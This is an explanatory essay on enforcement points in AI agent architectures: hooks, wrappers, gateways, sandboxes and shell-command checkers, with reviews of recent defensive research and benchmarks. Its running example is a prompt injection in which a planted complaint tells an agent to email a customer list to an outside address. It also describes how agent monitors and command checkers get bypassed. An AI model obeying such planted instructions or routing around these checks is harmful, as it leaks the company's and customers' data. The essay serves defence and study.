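# Where to place enforcement points in AI agent architectures

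## How an agent's output becomes an action, and where it can be stopped

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with tools, so its text can lead to actions such as changing a file, making a payment or sending an email. The model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, picks out the requests to use a tool, carries them out and feeds the results back to the model for the next round. A tool can be anything a program can call, from a database query to a web browser. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli et al., 2026) cites a count of 177,436 agent tools that developers created between November 2024 and February 2026 in public repositories for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface through which agents find and call tools on separate servers. A growing share of those tools make changes rather than only look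 up information.

An agent's actions take effect outside the model, so a defender can check them there. An enforcement point is a component that intercepts an action and either allows or blocks it before it takes effect. Actions pass through several layers of software, and a defender can put an enforcement point at any of them. The choice matters because different information about the action is available at each layer, and because an action may take a route that bypasses the check.

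Suppose a company has a support agent with access to a customer database, a workspace of files, a shell (a command line, here with Python), the web and email. An employee asks it to summarise this month's complaints and email the summary to Alice, a manager. One of the complaints contains an instruction, planted by someone outside the company, to send the customer list to an outside address. The company wants the agent to send Alice the summary without letting the customer list leave the company.

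### From text to effect

Early in the task, the agent takes the harmless step of fetching the complaints from the database with a short Python script.

The model first emits a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. Here the function is the shell and the argument is the text of the script. Nothing has run yet when the harness parses the call, and this is the first place where software can refuse it. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lets customers do this with a hook, a script of their own that runs after the model has written the arguments and before the harness processes the call. A sample hook from Anthropic reads the command in a shell call and returns "deny" if the command would delete a whole directory tree.

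Some tools run on a separate server. A gateway, which is a server between the agent and its tools, can block a call before it reaches them. In the example, the email tool might well sit behind a gateway. The shell probably runs on the agent's own machine, so its calls never reach the gateway.

Once the shell tool starts Python, the script makes a system call, a request to the core of the operating system, each time it reads a file, starts a process or opens a connection. The operating system can refuse the request, and so can a sandbox, an execution environment with outside limits on its access to files, processes and the network. The harness checks the code as one block, whereas the operating system receives each read, write and connection separately. Earlier monitors depend on structured calls with a known meaning and an explicit target, which a shell command does not provide. *Tether*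 (2026), a monitor for agents that work in a terminal, therefore infers actions such as "read", "copy" or "upload" from the system calls it observes.

The script's request then leaves the sandbox as network traffic, or egress, and a filter at the boundary can block it based on its destination. This may be the company's last chance to stop anything being sent to an outside party. *Kairos* (2026), which monitors agents at the input and output layer of the host machine, treats anything that affects an outside party as irreversible once sent.

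The request for the complaints stays inside the company, so one more check remains, at the database. The database receives a login with the query and can refuse the query if that login has no right to those rows. How useful this check is depends on whose login it is. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization*, guidance for Amazon's cloud customers, lists as a common mistake agent tools that do not pass on the user's identity. Every query then runs with the agent's own permissions, and the database cannot apply the user's.

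The agent could send out the customer list by more than one of these routes. A call to the email tool passes through the harness, perhaps a gateway, and the mail service, while a script run in the shell passes through the harness, the operating system and the network boundary. Checking outgoing mail at the gateway therefore does not stop the script from sending the list.

### Decisions and verdicts

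Deciding whether to stop an action and stopping it are separate jobs. In access control standards, the component that evaluates the policy and returns a verdict is the policy decision point (PDP), and the component that enforces the verdict is the policy enforcement point (PEP). A single program can do both jobs, but larger systems tend to split them. In Amazon's product, the gateway is the enforcement point, and a separate engine evaluates rules for every request. AWS also offers a log-only mode, which is a sensible way to test a policy on live traffic. The engine records what it would have permitted or denied, but the gateway lets every request through, so the policy gives no protection in this mode.

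A pre-execution decision is made before the action takes effect and can have four outcomes: allow, deny, ask a person, or modify. For the support agent's email tool, a policy might allow a message to Alice, deny one to an unknown outside address, ask the employee about one to a colleague the agent has never written to, and modify another by removing an attachment.

Many tools share the Model Context Protocol (MCP), whose specification (2026) describes them as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them on its own. The specification adds that there SHOULD always be a human who can deny an invocation, but "SHOULD" only marks a recommendation. It also mandates no particular way of involving the user, so a company that uses MCP cannot assume that anyone is approving tool calls.

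The monitor in *Kairos* can hold an effect and decide later whether to allow it, because a monitor that must decide immediately will either block legitimate work or let attacks through. This suits file changes, which the system can keep in a staging area until the monitor decides. An email can't be partly sent, so the monitor can only delay it.

### The reference monitor

The requirements for a good enforcement point predate AI agents by about half a century. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, dealt with shared computers on which people with different security clearances ran their own programs, some of them possibly hostile. Operating systems of the time had 100,000 instructions or more, too many for anyone to check. Much of that code had unrestricted access to the machine, and a flaw in any of it could give an attacker control.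 Anderson proposed putting the access checks in one small part of the system, the reference monitor, an idea the report credits to Lampson and to Graham and Denning. The monitor compares every reference that a running program makes to data, other programs or devices with what the program's user is allowed to do. It also checks the kind of access, since permission to read a file does not include permission to write to it.

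Anderson set three conditions for the mechanism that does this:

- it must be tamper-proof;
- it must always be invoked, including for the operating system's own programs;
- it must be small enough for analysis and tests to show that it is correct, a condition that later writers shorten to "verifiable".

The conditions apply almost unchanged when an agent takes the place of the hostile program. *Causality Laundering* (2026) claims all three for ARM, a proxy between an agent and its MCP server. Every tool call passes through the proxy. The proxy runs in a separate process, where the agent cannot alter the rules. It has four layers of deterministic checks that a tester can examine one at a time, and a denial from any layer is final. The first claim depends on a stated assumption that the deployment has no other path to the tools. The support agent would break that assumption, because a Python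 script in its shell can open a connection that bypasses the proxy. Improving the proxy cannot fix this, because whether a check is always invoked depends on everything else the agent can access.

In 1975, three years after Anderson, Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* gave the requirement its usual name, complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They meant the rule to cover start-up, recovery and maintenance as well as normal running, and they were suspicious of systems that save time by reusing the result of an earlier check, since the authority may have changed. For agents, Surapani and colleagues conclude that authority should be checked at each tool invocation, instead of being granted through one broad credential that the agent receives at the start and keeps.

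A second principle from the same paper is least privilege, which means that every program should run with only the rights its job requires. The support agent needs to read one month of complaints, work in one folder and send messages to Alice, but it can read the whole customer database, send messages to anyone and access the open web. If it had only the rights it needs, the planted instruction could do little harm even if the model followed it exactly.

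Saltzer and Schroeder also wanted decisions to rest on permission rather than exclusion, because mistakes are then easier to notice. A mistake in a list of permitted items (an allowlist) makes the system refuse something legitimate, and someone soon complains, whereas a mistake in a list of forbidden items can let something through for years without anyone noticing. The same reasoning applies when the decision point crashes or times out. The enforcement point can then fail closed (refuse the action) or fail open (let it run), and nobody reports the mistake if it fails open.

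### Confused deputies and prompt injection

Even a check that always runs can allow the wrong action. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy (1988) tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler kept usage statistics in a system directory, so the operators gave the compiler permission to write there. Users could also choose a file for debugging output, and one chose the billing file in the same directory. The operating system confirmed that the compiler had permission to write there, so the debugging output overwrote the company's billing records.

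The access check worked as designed. According to Hardy, the problem was that the compiler had authority from two sources, its operators and its user, and could not indicate which one a given request relied on. Hardy's remedy was the capability, an unforgeable ticket that both identifies a file and authorises access to it. The user would give the compiler a ticket for the output file, and a user who had no ticket for the billing file could not pass one to the compiler.

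The support agent is in the same position as the compiler. The company gave the agent a database login and a mail account, which the author of the complaint doesn't have. If the model follows the planted instruction, the agent still presents a valid login to the database and a valid account to the mail service. This is called prompt injection. The agent reads material that contains an instruction, and the model follows it as if it came from the user.

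Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, an older attack that gets a database to run text from a web form as a command. Developers largely fixed SQL injection with parameterised queries, which keep the command and the data apart so that the database never executes the data. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C doubts that a similar fix will ever exist for language models. The company's instructions, the employee's request and the complaint all reach the model as text in one prompt, and the model predicts the next token from all of it. Developers can mark the untrusted parts, train the model to give them less weight, or screen for suspicious phrases. These measures make a successful attack less likely, but they don't create a boundary between instructions and data. David C calls the language model an "inherently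 confusable deputy" and advises designers to assume the worst case, in which an attacker has direct access to the agent's tools, and to constrain the agent's actions with deterministic safeguards that are not language models.

David C also relays a simple rule from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from a party, its privileges drop to that party's. This rule would stop the leak, but read literally, it would also stop the task, because the agent has to read every complaint and a stranger who sends one has no right to read the others. A usable check must let the summary go to Alice and block the customer list from going to the outside address, so it needs more information than whether the agent has read something untrusted.

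### Instructions in the system prompt

The easiest defence to add is a line in the system prompt (the company's standing instructions to the model) that forbids sending customer data outside the company. The line is worth having, but it is not an enforcement point. The model receives it as text, alongside the complaint, and may or may not follow it. If the model emits the forbidden call anyway, the system prompt cannot intercept it.

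Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, used harmless file-deletion tasks to measure how often models emit a delete call when a false claim of authority in the agent's memory calls for one. One run used 50 wordings, 29 model endpoints and a system prompt that did not forbid deleting. The scoring rule that Leong fixed in advance counted only calls aimed at the protected directory or something inside it, and by that rule the models emitted a delete call in 1.21% of trials on average. A rule that Leong chose after seeing the data also counts calls on a parent directory, and gives 12.9%. Counting any delete call gives 20.2%. The three figures differ so widely for the same trials that none deserves much weight by itself.

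In a separate run, the system prompt granted read-only access and prohibited deletion outright, yet 15 models still emitted the delete call in 1.76% of 7,500 trials. Leong rated 14 of the 15 as resistant and reports that the failure largely disappears under restrictive prompts, so the instruction clearly does some good. All of these numbers warrant caution because Leong worked alone, picked models by availability, withdrew several claims from the paper's first version and released no code or data. But the argument does not need a precise rate. Leong found that the rate varied with the model, the wording, the system prompt and the period of testing, and a control that varies in this way cannot meet Anderson's third condition. An attacker can also keep sending complaints, even if 98 out of 100 attempts fail.

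There is wide agreement that an agent's actions should be checked outside the model. AWS tells customers that prompt instructions alone are not enough for authorisation, and that an external, deterministic check must finish before the tool executes. *ConfGuard* (2026), a monitor for agents that schedule industrial maintenance, describes a deterministic policy outside the model as the dominant pattern of defence in the research literature.

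Leong also tested a monitor of this kind, which admitted only memory records with a valid signature and confined deletions to the scope of a token. It rejected all 750 forged, altered, replayed or unsigned records, and in 1,350 trials the agent removed no file outside a token's scope, despite 83 attempts. Leong fairly presents this as a test that deterministic code works as written, which is a lower bar than resisting an attacker who adapts. But in 31 of 42 trials in which the deputy held a valid token, it induced deletions inside the permitted scope, and the monitor, like Hardy's operating system, had no basis for blocking them.

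An external check enforces only the policy someone has written for it. *Agenra* (2026), a language for authorising agents' tool calls, has a core with mathematical proofs about its functions. The agent can propose calls but cannot change the rules or issue approvals. But the monitor cannot enforce a requirement that is missing from the policy, and if a compromised address book returns the wrong address, the monitor will correctly follow its lookup rule and approve that address. Suppose the company's rule is that the support agent may send email. That rule allows the agent to send the message to Alice, but also to send the customer list to a stranger. To distinguish between them, the rule has to mention recipients or contents, and the enforcement point has to sit where it can read them.

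## Checking the tool call

A program can enforce a rule about recipients only where it can read them, and the tool call is the first place it can. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) checks tool calls because each call has a tool name and typed arguments, which a program can compare with a rule. The model's reasoning is free text, so comparing it with a rule would require another model.

### One rule and two calls

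Suppose the support agent's email tool takes three lists of recipients (to, cc and bcc), a subject, a body and attachments. For the employee's task, the company could write this rule:

```
allow send_email
  when every address in to, cc and bcc is in task.recipients
   and attachments is empty
otherwise refuse: "This task may only email people the employee named."
```

The enforcement point first has to intercept the tool call and hold it until the check allows or denies it. A check that runs alongside the tool can log the call but can't block it.

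Next it validates the arguments and puts them in a standard form. It refuses a call with missing or unknown fields, strips display names from addresses and converts the addresses to lower case, so that "Alice <Alice@Company.example>" becomes alice@company.example. Arguments can also contain deeply nested text. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a checker that extracts up to 10,000 pieces of text, down to 32 levels of nesting, and flags the call as suspicious if any text is left over. Flagging the call is the right default because the checker can't tell whether text it hasn't examined is safe.

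The rule also depends on the list `task.recipients`, which is not in the call. The harness has to build this list from the employee's request and the company directory before the agent opens any complaint. If the model could fill it in later, the planted instruction could make it add an address. The same goes for the user's identity, the agent's identity and the time. Surapani and colleagues point out that the company and the user are separate sources of authority, because a company may give an agent tools that a particular user has no right to use. So a rule may need facts about both.

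The legitimate call sends the summary to Alice with no attachment, so both conditions hold and the email goes out. The planted call sends the customer list to records@outside.example, which is not in `task.recipients`. No rule allows this, so the check blocks the call without having to determine whether someone has deceived the model. Another call might address the email to Alice and put the outside address in bcc. The check blocks this too, but only because the rule covers all three fields.

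*Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) sets out a fuller sequence for the Open Agent Passport (OAP), a specification for checks of this kind. Each agent has a signed passport that lists what it may do and within what limits. The check refuses the call if the passport is inactive, if it doesn't list the capability, if no policy exists for that capability, or if nobody has verified the agent's owner to the required level. If none of these applies, the check tests the arguments against the rules. A call that passes every test runs, unless the passport requires a person's approval. The reference implementation doesn't yet support approvals, so a company that wants them would have to add them.

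An agent can continue its task after a call is refused. By default, Progent returns an error message with the reason and a reminder of the user's original request, so the support agent could still write to Alice after its outside email is refused. A rule can instead stop the agent or let the user decide. If the enforcement point rewrites a call, it should also check the new version.

### Hook, wrapper or gateway

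The same rule can run in three positions.

A hook inside the harness receives the calls that the model makes through that harness, including calls to built-in tools such as the shell. Uchibeke lists hooks in Claude Code, Cursor, LangChain and CrewAI that OAP already uses in production. These hooks work only if the harness invokes them correctly, which OAP explicitly assumes. A company should also confirm that the hook runs for every tool. The one listed for Cursor is called `beforeShellExecution`, which suggests that it doesn't cover email.

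A wrapper replaces a tool's function with a version that runs the check first. Progent's library mode works this way and takes a few lines of code. It protects built-in tools too, but if a developer adds a tool and forgets to wrap it, that tool is unguarded.

A gateway checks calls on their way to MCP servers. In Progent's proxy mode, the user changes the addresses the agent uses to reach its model and MCP servers, without changing the agent's code. This may work even for closed-source products. However, Shi and colleagues acknowledge that the proxy cannot protect built-in tools that don't use MCP. Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Policy, the product with the log-only mode, is a commercial example of a check at a gateway.

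| Position | Can it rewrite a call? | What skips it? | Does it serve many agents? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hook in the harness | Yes, if the harness accepts changed arguments | Tools for which the hook doesn't fire; programs outside the harness | No, each harness needs its own |
| Wrapper around a tool | Yes | Unwrapped tools; code that contacts the service directly | Only agents that share the wrapped code |
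| Gateway | Yes, before forwarding it | Built-in tools; any direct connection to the service | Yes |

Aegis, built by Yuan and colleagues, patches the software library through which an agent communicates with its model and holds each tool call there while a central server decides whether to allow it. Yuan and colleagues call the server a gateway, but the tool calls don't pass through it, so in standard terms it is a decision point. This design lets one set of rules cover agents built on 14 frameworks. Enforcement still happens in each agent's own software, however, and Yuan and colleagues say that Aegis doesn't defend against calls made outside the patched library.

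For the support agent, a gateway is a sensible place to enforce the email rule, because other agents in the company probably send email too. The shell bypasses the gateway, so it needs a hook or a wrapper.

### Progent: a policy for each task

The example rule suits one task. Another employee may want the agent to write to a customer, and a rule loose enough for every task would permit the leak. Progent therefore writes a new policy for each task and adjusts it as the agent learns more.

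A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool when the call's arguments meet stated conditions, and specifies what to do if it blocks a call. The conditions can compare numbers, test whether a value is in a list, measure the length of a list or match text against a pattern. Progent applies the "forbid" rules first, then the "allow" rules, and blocks a call that matches no rule. A company can also set policies for all tasks, and a task's own policy cannot permit what these forbid.

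A language model drafts the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before it has read anything from outside. Shi and colleagues assume that the user is honest. But the request often doesn't reveal everything the task will need. If the employee had asked the agent to follow the instructions in an email from Alice, nobody could write the full policy before the agent had opened that email. So after a tool call, a language model decides, without seeing the tool's result, whether the policy might need to change. If so, a model reads the result and drafts a new policy.

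That second draft is risky, because the result may contain a planted instruction. Progent therefore compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions. Write A(P) for the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. The new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

meaning that it allows nothing the old one didn't. Progent applies a narrowing automatically. Any other change counts as an expansion and needs approval, even if the new policy is shorter. Replacing Alice's address with a stranger's is an expansion, because the old policy allowed no email to the stranger. Between approvals the set of permitted calls can therefore only shrink or stay the same, a property that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement.

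Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of banking, travel, Slack and office tasks with attacks planted in the material that the agent reads. GPT-4o ran the agent and wrote the policies. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench (ASB), Progent cut the success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. They report that agents completed about as many legitimate tasks as before on both benchmarks, and plot these rates without discussing individual percentages. On AgentDojo, an older defence that removed whole tools and ignored their arguments let more attacks succeed and completed fewer legitimate tasks, because it either removed a tool that the task needed or left the tool open to the attacker.

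To imitate a careless user, the main experiments approved every expansion automatically, so the solver's verdict never stopped anything. The 1.0% therefore measures how well GPT-4o writes policies, including policies drafted from text that contains an attack, and doesn't test monotonic confinement. GPT-4o writes these policies surprisingly well, and three kinds of attack aimed at the policy updates raised the success rate only marginally. With the first policy frozen for the whole task, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. Refusing all expansions gave the lowest rate of any automatic setting, and a security-conscious person who reviewed the first policy and every expansion brought it to zero. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer's workload looks manageable, at least on these tasks.

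*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that people make mistakes writing policies by hand, and that hostile text in a tool's result may lead to an update that loosens the rules. The solver addresses the second problem only if someone or something rejects bad expansions of what the rules allow.

The benchmark results also depend on the model. Without Progent, 6.8% of the AgentDojo attacks succeeded against Claude Sonnet 4, and Progent cut this to 0.5%. That is still a large proportional reduction, but a company with a recent model shouldn't expect the 39-percentage-point reduction seen with GPT-4o. Shi and colleagues also left out two attacks that steered an AI travel agent towards a different but legitimate hotel. This was fair because a person couldn't have spotted the trick either, but the figures therefore exclude attacks that stay within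 the agent's permissions.

### Other ways to get the rules

A company could write all its rules in advance. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) offers a small language for this, in which each rule has a trigger, a check and a response. In one example, a bank transfer triggers a rule that checks whether the recipient is outside the family and, if so, asks the user. A rule can also stop the agent, run a substitute action or tell the model to reconsider. Telling the model to reconsider gives weaker protection than the other responses because the model still makes the decision.

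Wang and colleagues tested AgentSpec on three kinds of agent. The first received 750 requests for risky code, 30 in each of 25 categories. It tried to run a program 422 times, and the rules flagged 333 of those programs, or 79%. Wang and colleagues report over 90%, which is about right if two categories are excluded because the agent's code did not contain the requested flaw. After inspecting the flagged programs, they judged 58 harmless. The second agent controlled a household robot. The rules stopped every hazardous task, while completion of safe tasks fell from 58.62% to 54.26%. The third agent, a self-driving system, obeyed the law in all the scenarios where it had previously broken it.

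These results are less impressive than they sound, because the code rules were written from descriptions of the same risks that the test contained. The experiment with rules written by OpenAI's o1 model is more informative because, for the code and robot agents, it used examples that o1 hadn't been shown. Those rules caught 87.26% of the risky code. For the robot, 95.56% of the actions the rules flagged were hazardous, but the rules missed 29% of the hazards. They prevented violations in five of the eight driving scenarios.

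Aegis relies mainly on 22 patterns of known attacks in seven categories, such as database commands hidden in an argument or paths to password files. It blocked all 48 attacks in a suite that Yuan and colleagues built from documented techniques. It also wrongly flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls, all six of which were database queries containing an ordinary "or". As the researchers accept, blocking every known attack is little evidence that Aegis would block new ones. Patterns are also a poor fit for the support agent, because the planted email is normal except for its destination. A pattern for personal data might catch the customer list, but it could just as easily flag a summary for Alice that quotes one customer's address.

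The third option is to learn the rules from normal use. *AgentGuardian* (Abaev, Klimov and colleagues, 2026) recorded 60 harmless runs of each of two applications, a research assistant and an IT support agent. It groups similar inputs and turns each group into a text pattern with limits on properties such as length and time of day. It also learns which tools normally follow one another. Each agent gets its own rules for each tool, because an IT agent has reasons to read system files that a research assistant doesn't.

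AgentGuardian caught 18 of 20 bad inputs. It wrongly refused 8 of 80 harmless runs and flagged another 6 in which the model itself made a mistake, such as inventing a file name. The sample of 20 bad inputs is very small, and some were easy to catch, including an email address with two @ signs. The method also assumes that nobody attacks the agent during the recording period.

A sample rule in the paper shows why someone should read learned rules before using them. According to its caption, the rule limits the research assistant to text files in two folders, and further restricts file names in one of them. But the printed pattern lists three alternatives, and the third accepts any path without spaces that begins with "./" and ends in ".txt", so the restrictions in the first two have no effect. Abaev and colleagues found that rules learned from 10 runs accepted almost any text, and that more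 recordings produce tighter rules.

### What the payment tests measured

A public contest tested checks on tool calls by having people try to talk an AI agent at a simulated bank into paying them. In *Before the Tool Call*, Uchibeke, whose company APort Technologies ran the contest, reports that 74.6% of attacks fooled the model under a permissive policy, but none of 879 attempts got through under a strict OAP policy.

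That comparison shows very little. In a follow-up paper, *APort Vault*, Uchibeke (2026) explains that the 879 attempts took place at a level where the passport granted no permission to pay anyone. The check refused every payment because its policy allowed none. The two figures also come from different attempts under different policies, so the gap between them cannot measure the effect of adding a check.

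The follow-up is much better. Uchibeke replayed 4,371 attack attempts from the contest against 14 models, including GPT-6 Astra and Claude Fable 5.1, with and without the check. At the three levels where the policy allowed payments to some recipients and not others, the models made 140 forbidden payments in 76,842 runs (0.18%) without the check and none in 69,297 runs with it. The check still allowed other payments, and 25,370 of the runs with it included a successful one. It evaluated 25,640 payment calls and denied 187, of which 148 were for a forbidden recipient.

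Many of the runs behind the zero replay messages from the same session, so they are not independent, and Uchibeke sensibly counts the 790 sessions instead. When an event never occurs in S independent trials, 3/S is a rough upper limit on its true rate at 95% confidence, which here gives 3/790, or 0.38% of sessions. A more basic limitation is that the experiment and the check used the same rule, which forbade payments to any recipient not on the list. The zero therefore shows that the check ran every time and worked as written, but like Leong's test of a similar monitor, it can't show that the list was the right rule. The test also covered only one payment tool in one simulated bank and was run by the vendor, though Uchibeke has released the data and the scoring code.

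The results for the models alone may be more useful. The failure rate was only 0.18%, but the failures were clustered. Two of the 790 sessions produced half of them, and one family of attacks, based on forged receipts, caused most of the failures at one level. An attacker who finds a message that works can send it again, so the average failure rate across all attackers understates the risk from a skilled one.

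### What the arguments leave out

At the strictest of these three levels, the models requested a payment in 79.4% of runs without the check. Most of these payments went to the approved recipient, so they complied with the policy. Uchibeke notes that a permitted payment isn't necessarily legitimate. The recipient's name doesn't show whether anyone at the bank wanted the payment made.

Some tools are so broad that their arguments hardly constrain anything. If the support agent's database tool accepts any query, enforcing a rule requires interpreting the query, and shell commands are even harder to interpret. Abaev and colleagues concede that text patterns cannot reliably separate harmless from hostile instructions in free text. It is often better to change the tool. A tool called `get_complaints`, whose only argument is a month, needs a very simple rule and cannot return the customer list if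 its code only reads complaints. This moves part of the policy into the tool's code, which the company must protect and test like any other part of the check.

Even a narrow tool can have effects that its arguments don't show. An email to managers@company.example looks internal, but the list may include an outside consultant, or Alice's account may forward her mail elsewhere. An attachment called summary.pdf could contain anything, and a check that receives only the file name cannot inspect the contents. This is one reason the example rule bans all attachments. OAP's stated limits include both problems, since it does not defend against unintended side effects of permitted actions or examine their content. A rule can catch some side effects, for example by expanding mailing lists before it compares addresses, but only those its author anticipated.

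The check also depends on the tool doing what its description claims. People write rules from these descriptions, and so does the model in Progent. Most of Progent's remaining failures on ASB involved attack tools with names and descriptions much like those of legitimate ones. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could have told them apart without knowing in advance which tools to trust. When they wrote rules by hand with that knowledge, no attack succeeded. Anyone who installs tools from public collections faces this risk. Uchibeke cites Cisco researchers who found more than 824 malicious add-ons, about a fifth of the total, in the registry for OpenClaw, an open agent framework.

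A tool's description can also become false without malice. Suppose the `send_email` tool sits on an MCP server that another team runs, and an update makes it copy every message to an outside archiving service. The call looks the same as before, so the check approves it. The company should allow only tools that someone has reviewed, record the exact definition they reviewed, and refuse calls if the server later presents a different one. This catches a changed description or a new argument, but not a code change that leaves the definition the same, so for tools that handle customer data the company also needs to control which version of the code runs.

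## Checking shell commands and generated code

A rule that checks arguments works well for an email tool because the arguments include the recipients, but a shell tool's main argument is a program. The support agent's script for fetching complaints could loop over every row in the database, write each one to a file and email the files to a hundred people. The harness would still receive a single tool call, and approving it would do very little to limit what the script does.

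Sometimes a tool call doesn't contain the program it runs. If the agent saves a script as summarise.py in one step and runs it in the next, the second call contains only a file name. According to lecture slides from UT Austin, rules at this layer govern tool calls, "not the processes they start". The University of Vermont says Claude Code checks its permission rules before a tool runs and relies on the operating system to limit shell commands and the processes they start.

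### What a checker can know in advance

A checker could work out what many scripts will do by reading them, but not what every script will do. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no program can determine, for every program, whether that program will finish. If a checker could always determine whether a script will send an email, it could be used to do what Turing proved impossible. Any program that sends no email can be given an extra line at the end that sends one. The modified program sends the email exactly when the original program finishes, so the checker's answer would reveal whether the original finishes. The same argument applies to deleting a file or opening a connection.

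Even a short script can depend on facts that are not in its text, such as which files exist or what a web server returns.

Turing's proof rules out a checker that always gives a correct yes or no, but not one that can also return "cannot tell". The safe response to that result is to refuse the script or ask a person. A checker that never lets a harmful script through must also stop some harmless ones, and how many it stops depends on how much it can determine about what a script does.

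### Matching the text of a command

The simplest check compares the command with a list of patterns. In Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, each rule gives the first words of a command, and the harness checks whether the command it is about to run starts with them. One rule that OpenAI uses on its own machines lets the agent run a program to view or list proposed code changes on GitHub, but doesn't cover the other things that program can do.

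OpenAI warns that one string can hide several actions. Codex splits a script into separate commands if it is a plain chain with no variables or wildcards. The strictest verdict on any command then applies to the whole script (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI Execution Policy Rules*). Codex judges a more complex script as one unit, which is reasonable as long as a person must approve any script that matches no rule.

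Short lists of text patterns miss most dangerous commands. In *CARE*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) tested checkers on 220 dangerous commands, most of them from public collections of attack tests, and 329 ordinary ones. A set of 22 patterns caught 17% of the dangerous commands and blocked none of the ordinary ones. Their own checker, CARE, caught 76% of the dangerous commands and wrongly blocked 0.9% of the ordinary ones.

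CARE first rewrites the command in a standard form, which removes wrappers and undoes simple encodings. It then gives the command four scores between 0 and 1, for the kind of action, the sensitivity of the files involved, any match with a known attack pattern, and the structure of the command:

score = 0.3 × action + 0.3 × files + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

CARE allows a command that scores below 0.15 and denies one that scores 0.35 or more. For scores in between, it denies the command if one piece of evidence is strong enough and otherwise sends it to a language model. Only 23 of the 549 commands went to the model. The scores for action and files contribute the most. In the version without the language model, removing the action score cut the share of dangerous commands caught from 76% to 42%, and removing the file score cut it to 53%. This makes sense, because commands that read system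 files are usually routine, unlike commands that change them.

A checker that stops three-quarters of dangerous commands is useful against an agent's mistakes but is a weak barrier to an attacker who keeps trying. In Liu and colleagues' example of 10,000 commands, of which 1% are dangerous, CARE stops 76 dangerous commands, misses 24 and blocks about 90 harmless ones. Stricter settings block more harmless commands. In the version without the language model, lowering the first threshold to 0.10 raises the catch rate to 97% but blocks 23% of ordinary commands.

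The language model also weakened protection in one test. Liu and colleagues had a model write 600 commands from malicious instructions and ran them in a sandbox. With no check, 75% ran successfully. CARE's fixed rules cut this to 37%, but adding the language model raised it to 53% because the model approved commands that the rules had flagged. The same model had written the commands, which may be why it approved them. A company that cares more about blocking attacks than avoiding false alarms should probably use the fixed rules alone.

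CARE checks one command at a time, plus some information about the files it names, so it cannot detect a plan spread over several harmless-looking commands. Any check on text also assumes that the checker and the shell interpret the text the same way, though each parses it separately, and that the named program does only what the rule's writer had in mind. *ParseGap* (Li, 2026) compared the verdicts of the command checkers in eight production coding agents with what the shell then did, and every checker approved some commands with effects that the policy prohibited. The UT Austin slides call command-blocking patterns guardrails against accidents, which seems about right.

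Given these errors, approving a command shouldn't switch off other protections. OpenAI's rules let common harmless commands run without approval and outside the sandbox, so one mistaken rule could remove both safeguards. Li recommends never loosening the sandbox around a command because it was approved.

### Resolving a command to its action and objects

A checker can instead work out which operation a command would perform and which objects it would actually affect. Suppose the support agent proposes to delete reports/old.txt. A pattern might allow this because the agent is allowed to change anything in the reports folder. But "reports" could be a link to a folder elsewhere on the machine, in which case the command would delete a file that the agent isn't allowed to change. A checker can detect this by following the link before it allows the command.

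*What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know* (Jing, 2026), an October 2026 preprint by a single independent researcher, describes and tests a checker of this kind. One component turns the command into a verb and its operands, and follows links to find the files the operands refer to. If the command contains a construct it cannot enumerate, such as a pipeline, the component reports the command as undecidable. The component also splits a series of statements into separate actions. The gate denies the whole series if it denies any part, and sends the series for review if the parts affect more than one object.

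The gate reads only the resolved action and returns allow, ask or deny. It has seven rules:

- it fails closed if it cannot resolve the command or has an internal error;
- it treats some verbs as sensitive, based on their effect and not their name;
- it identifies a program by its name, its position in the command and the contents of its file, so it can recognise a renamed copy;
- it checks whether each target lies in a permitted zone of the filesystem;
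- it protects the top folder of the workspace;
- it considers how many objects the command affects, including any that a wildcard adds;
- it requires the objects that the agent declared in advance to cover every object the command would touch.

The last rule would help the support agent's employer, because a declaration that the agent will write summary.txt doesn't cover a command that also touches the customer list. After an approval, the gate issues a single-use credential limited to the approved verb, files and arguments, so the agent can't reuse the approval for something else.

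Jing finalized 61 test cases in advance, and the gate gave the right verdict on all of them, both with and without declared objects. Since Jing wrote both the rules and the cases, this mainly shows that the gate does what its author intended. To check whether the tests could detect a broken gate, Jing introduced 50 deliberate faults and ran the tests on each faulty version. The tests detected 46. Three of the missed faults revealed gaps in the test cases, and whether the tests detect the fourth depends on which files are on the machine. This result measures the tests, not the gate, but it makes the gate's perfect score more credible.

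The gate looks worse on 216 commands that Jing carried over from an earlier study of Windows. It allowed 30 that it should have stopped according to that study. Jing attributes 20 of these to the conversion to Linux and the other 10 to a difference in policy, because the Windows version protected certain names and the Linux version protects zones. Jing thinks only those 10 could be blind spots in the gate, but had predicted none.

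In the most important experiment, Jing ran 65 short scripts, 57 that should be denied and 8 that were harmless, and compared the files on the machine before and after each run. Without the gate, 25 scripts had effects that the policy forbids, but with it none did, and all 8 harmless scripts still ran. The hook passed the gate the text of each script rather than the command that starts it, which would have shown only a file name. An operating-system profile with the same policy did not prevent 8 of the 25 harmful effects.

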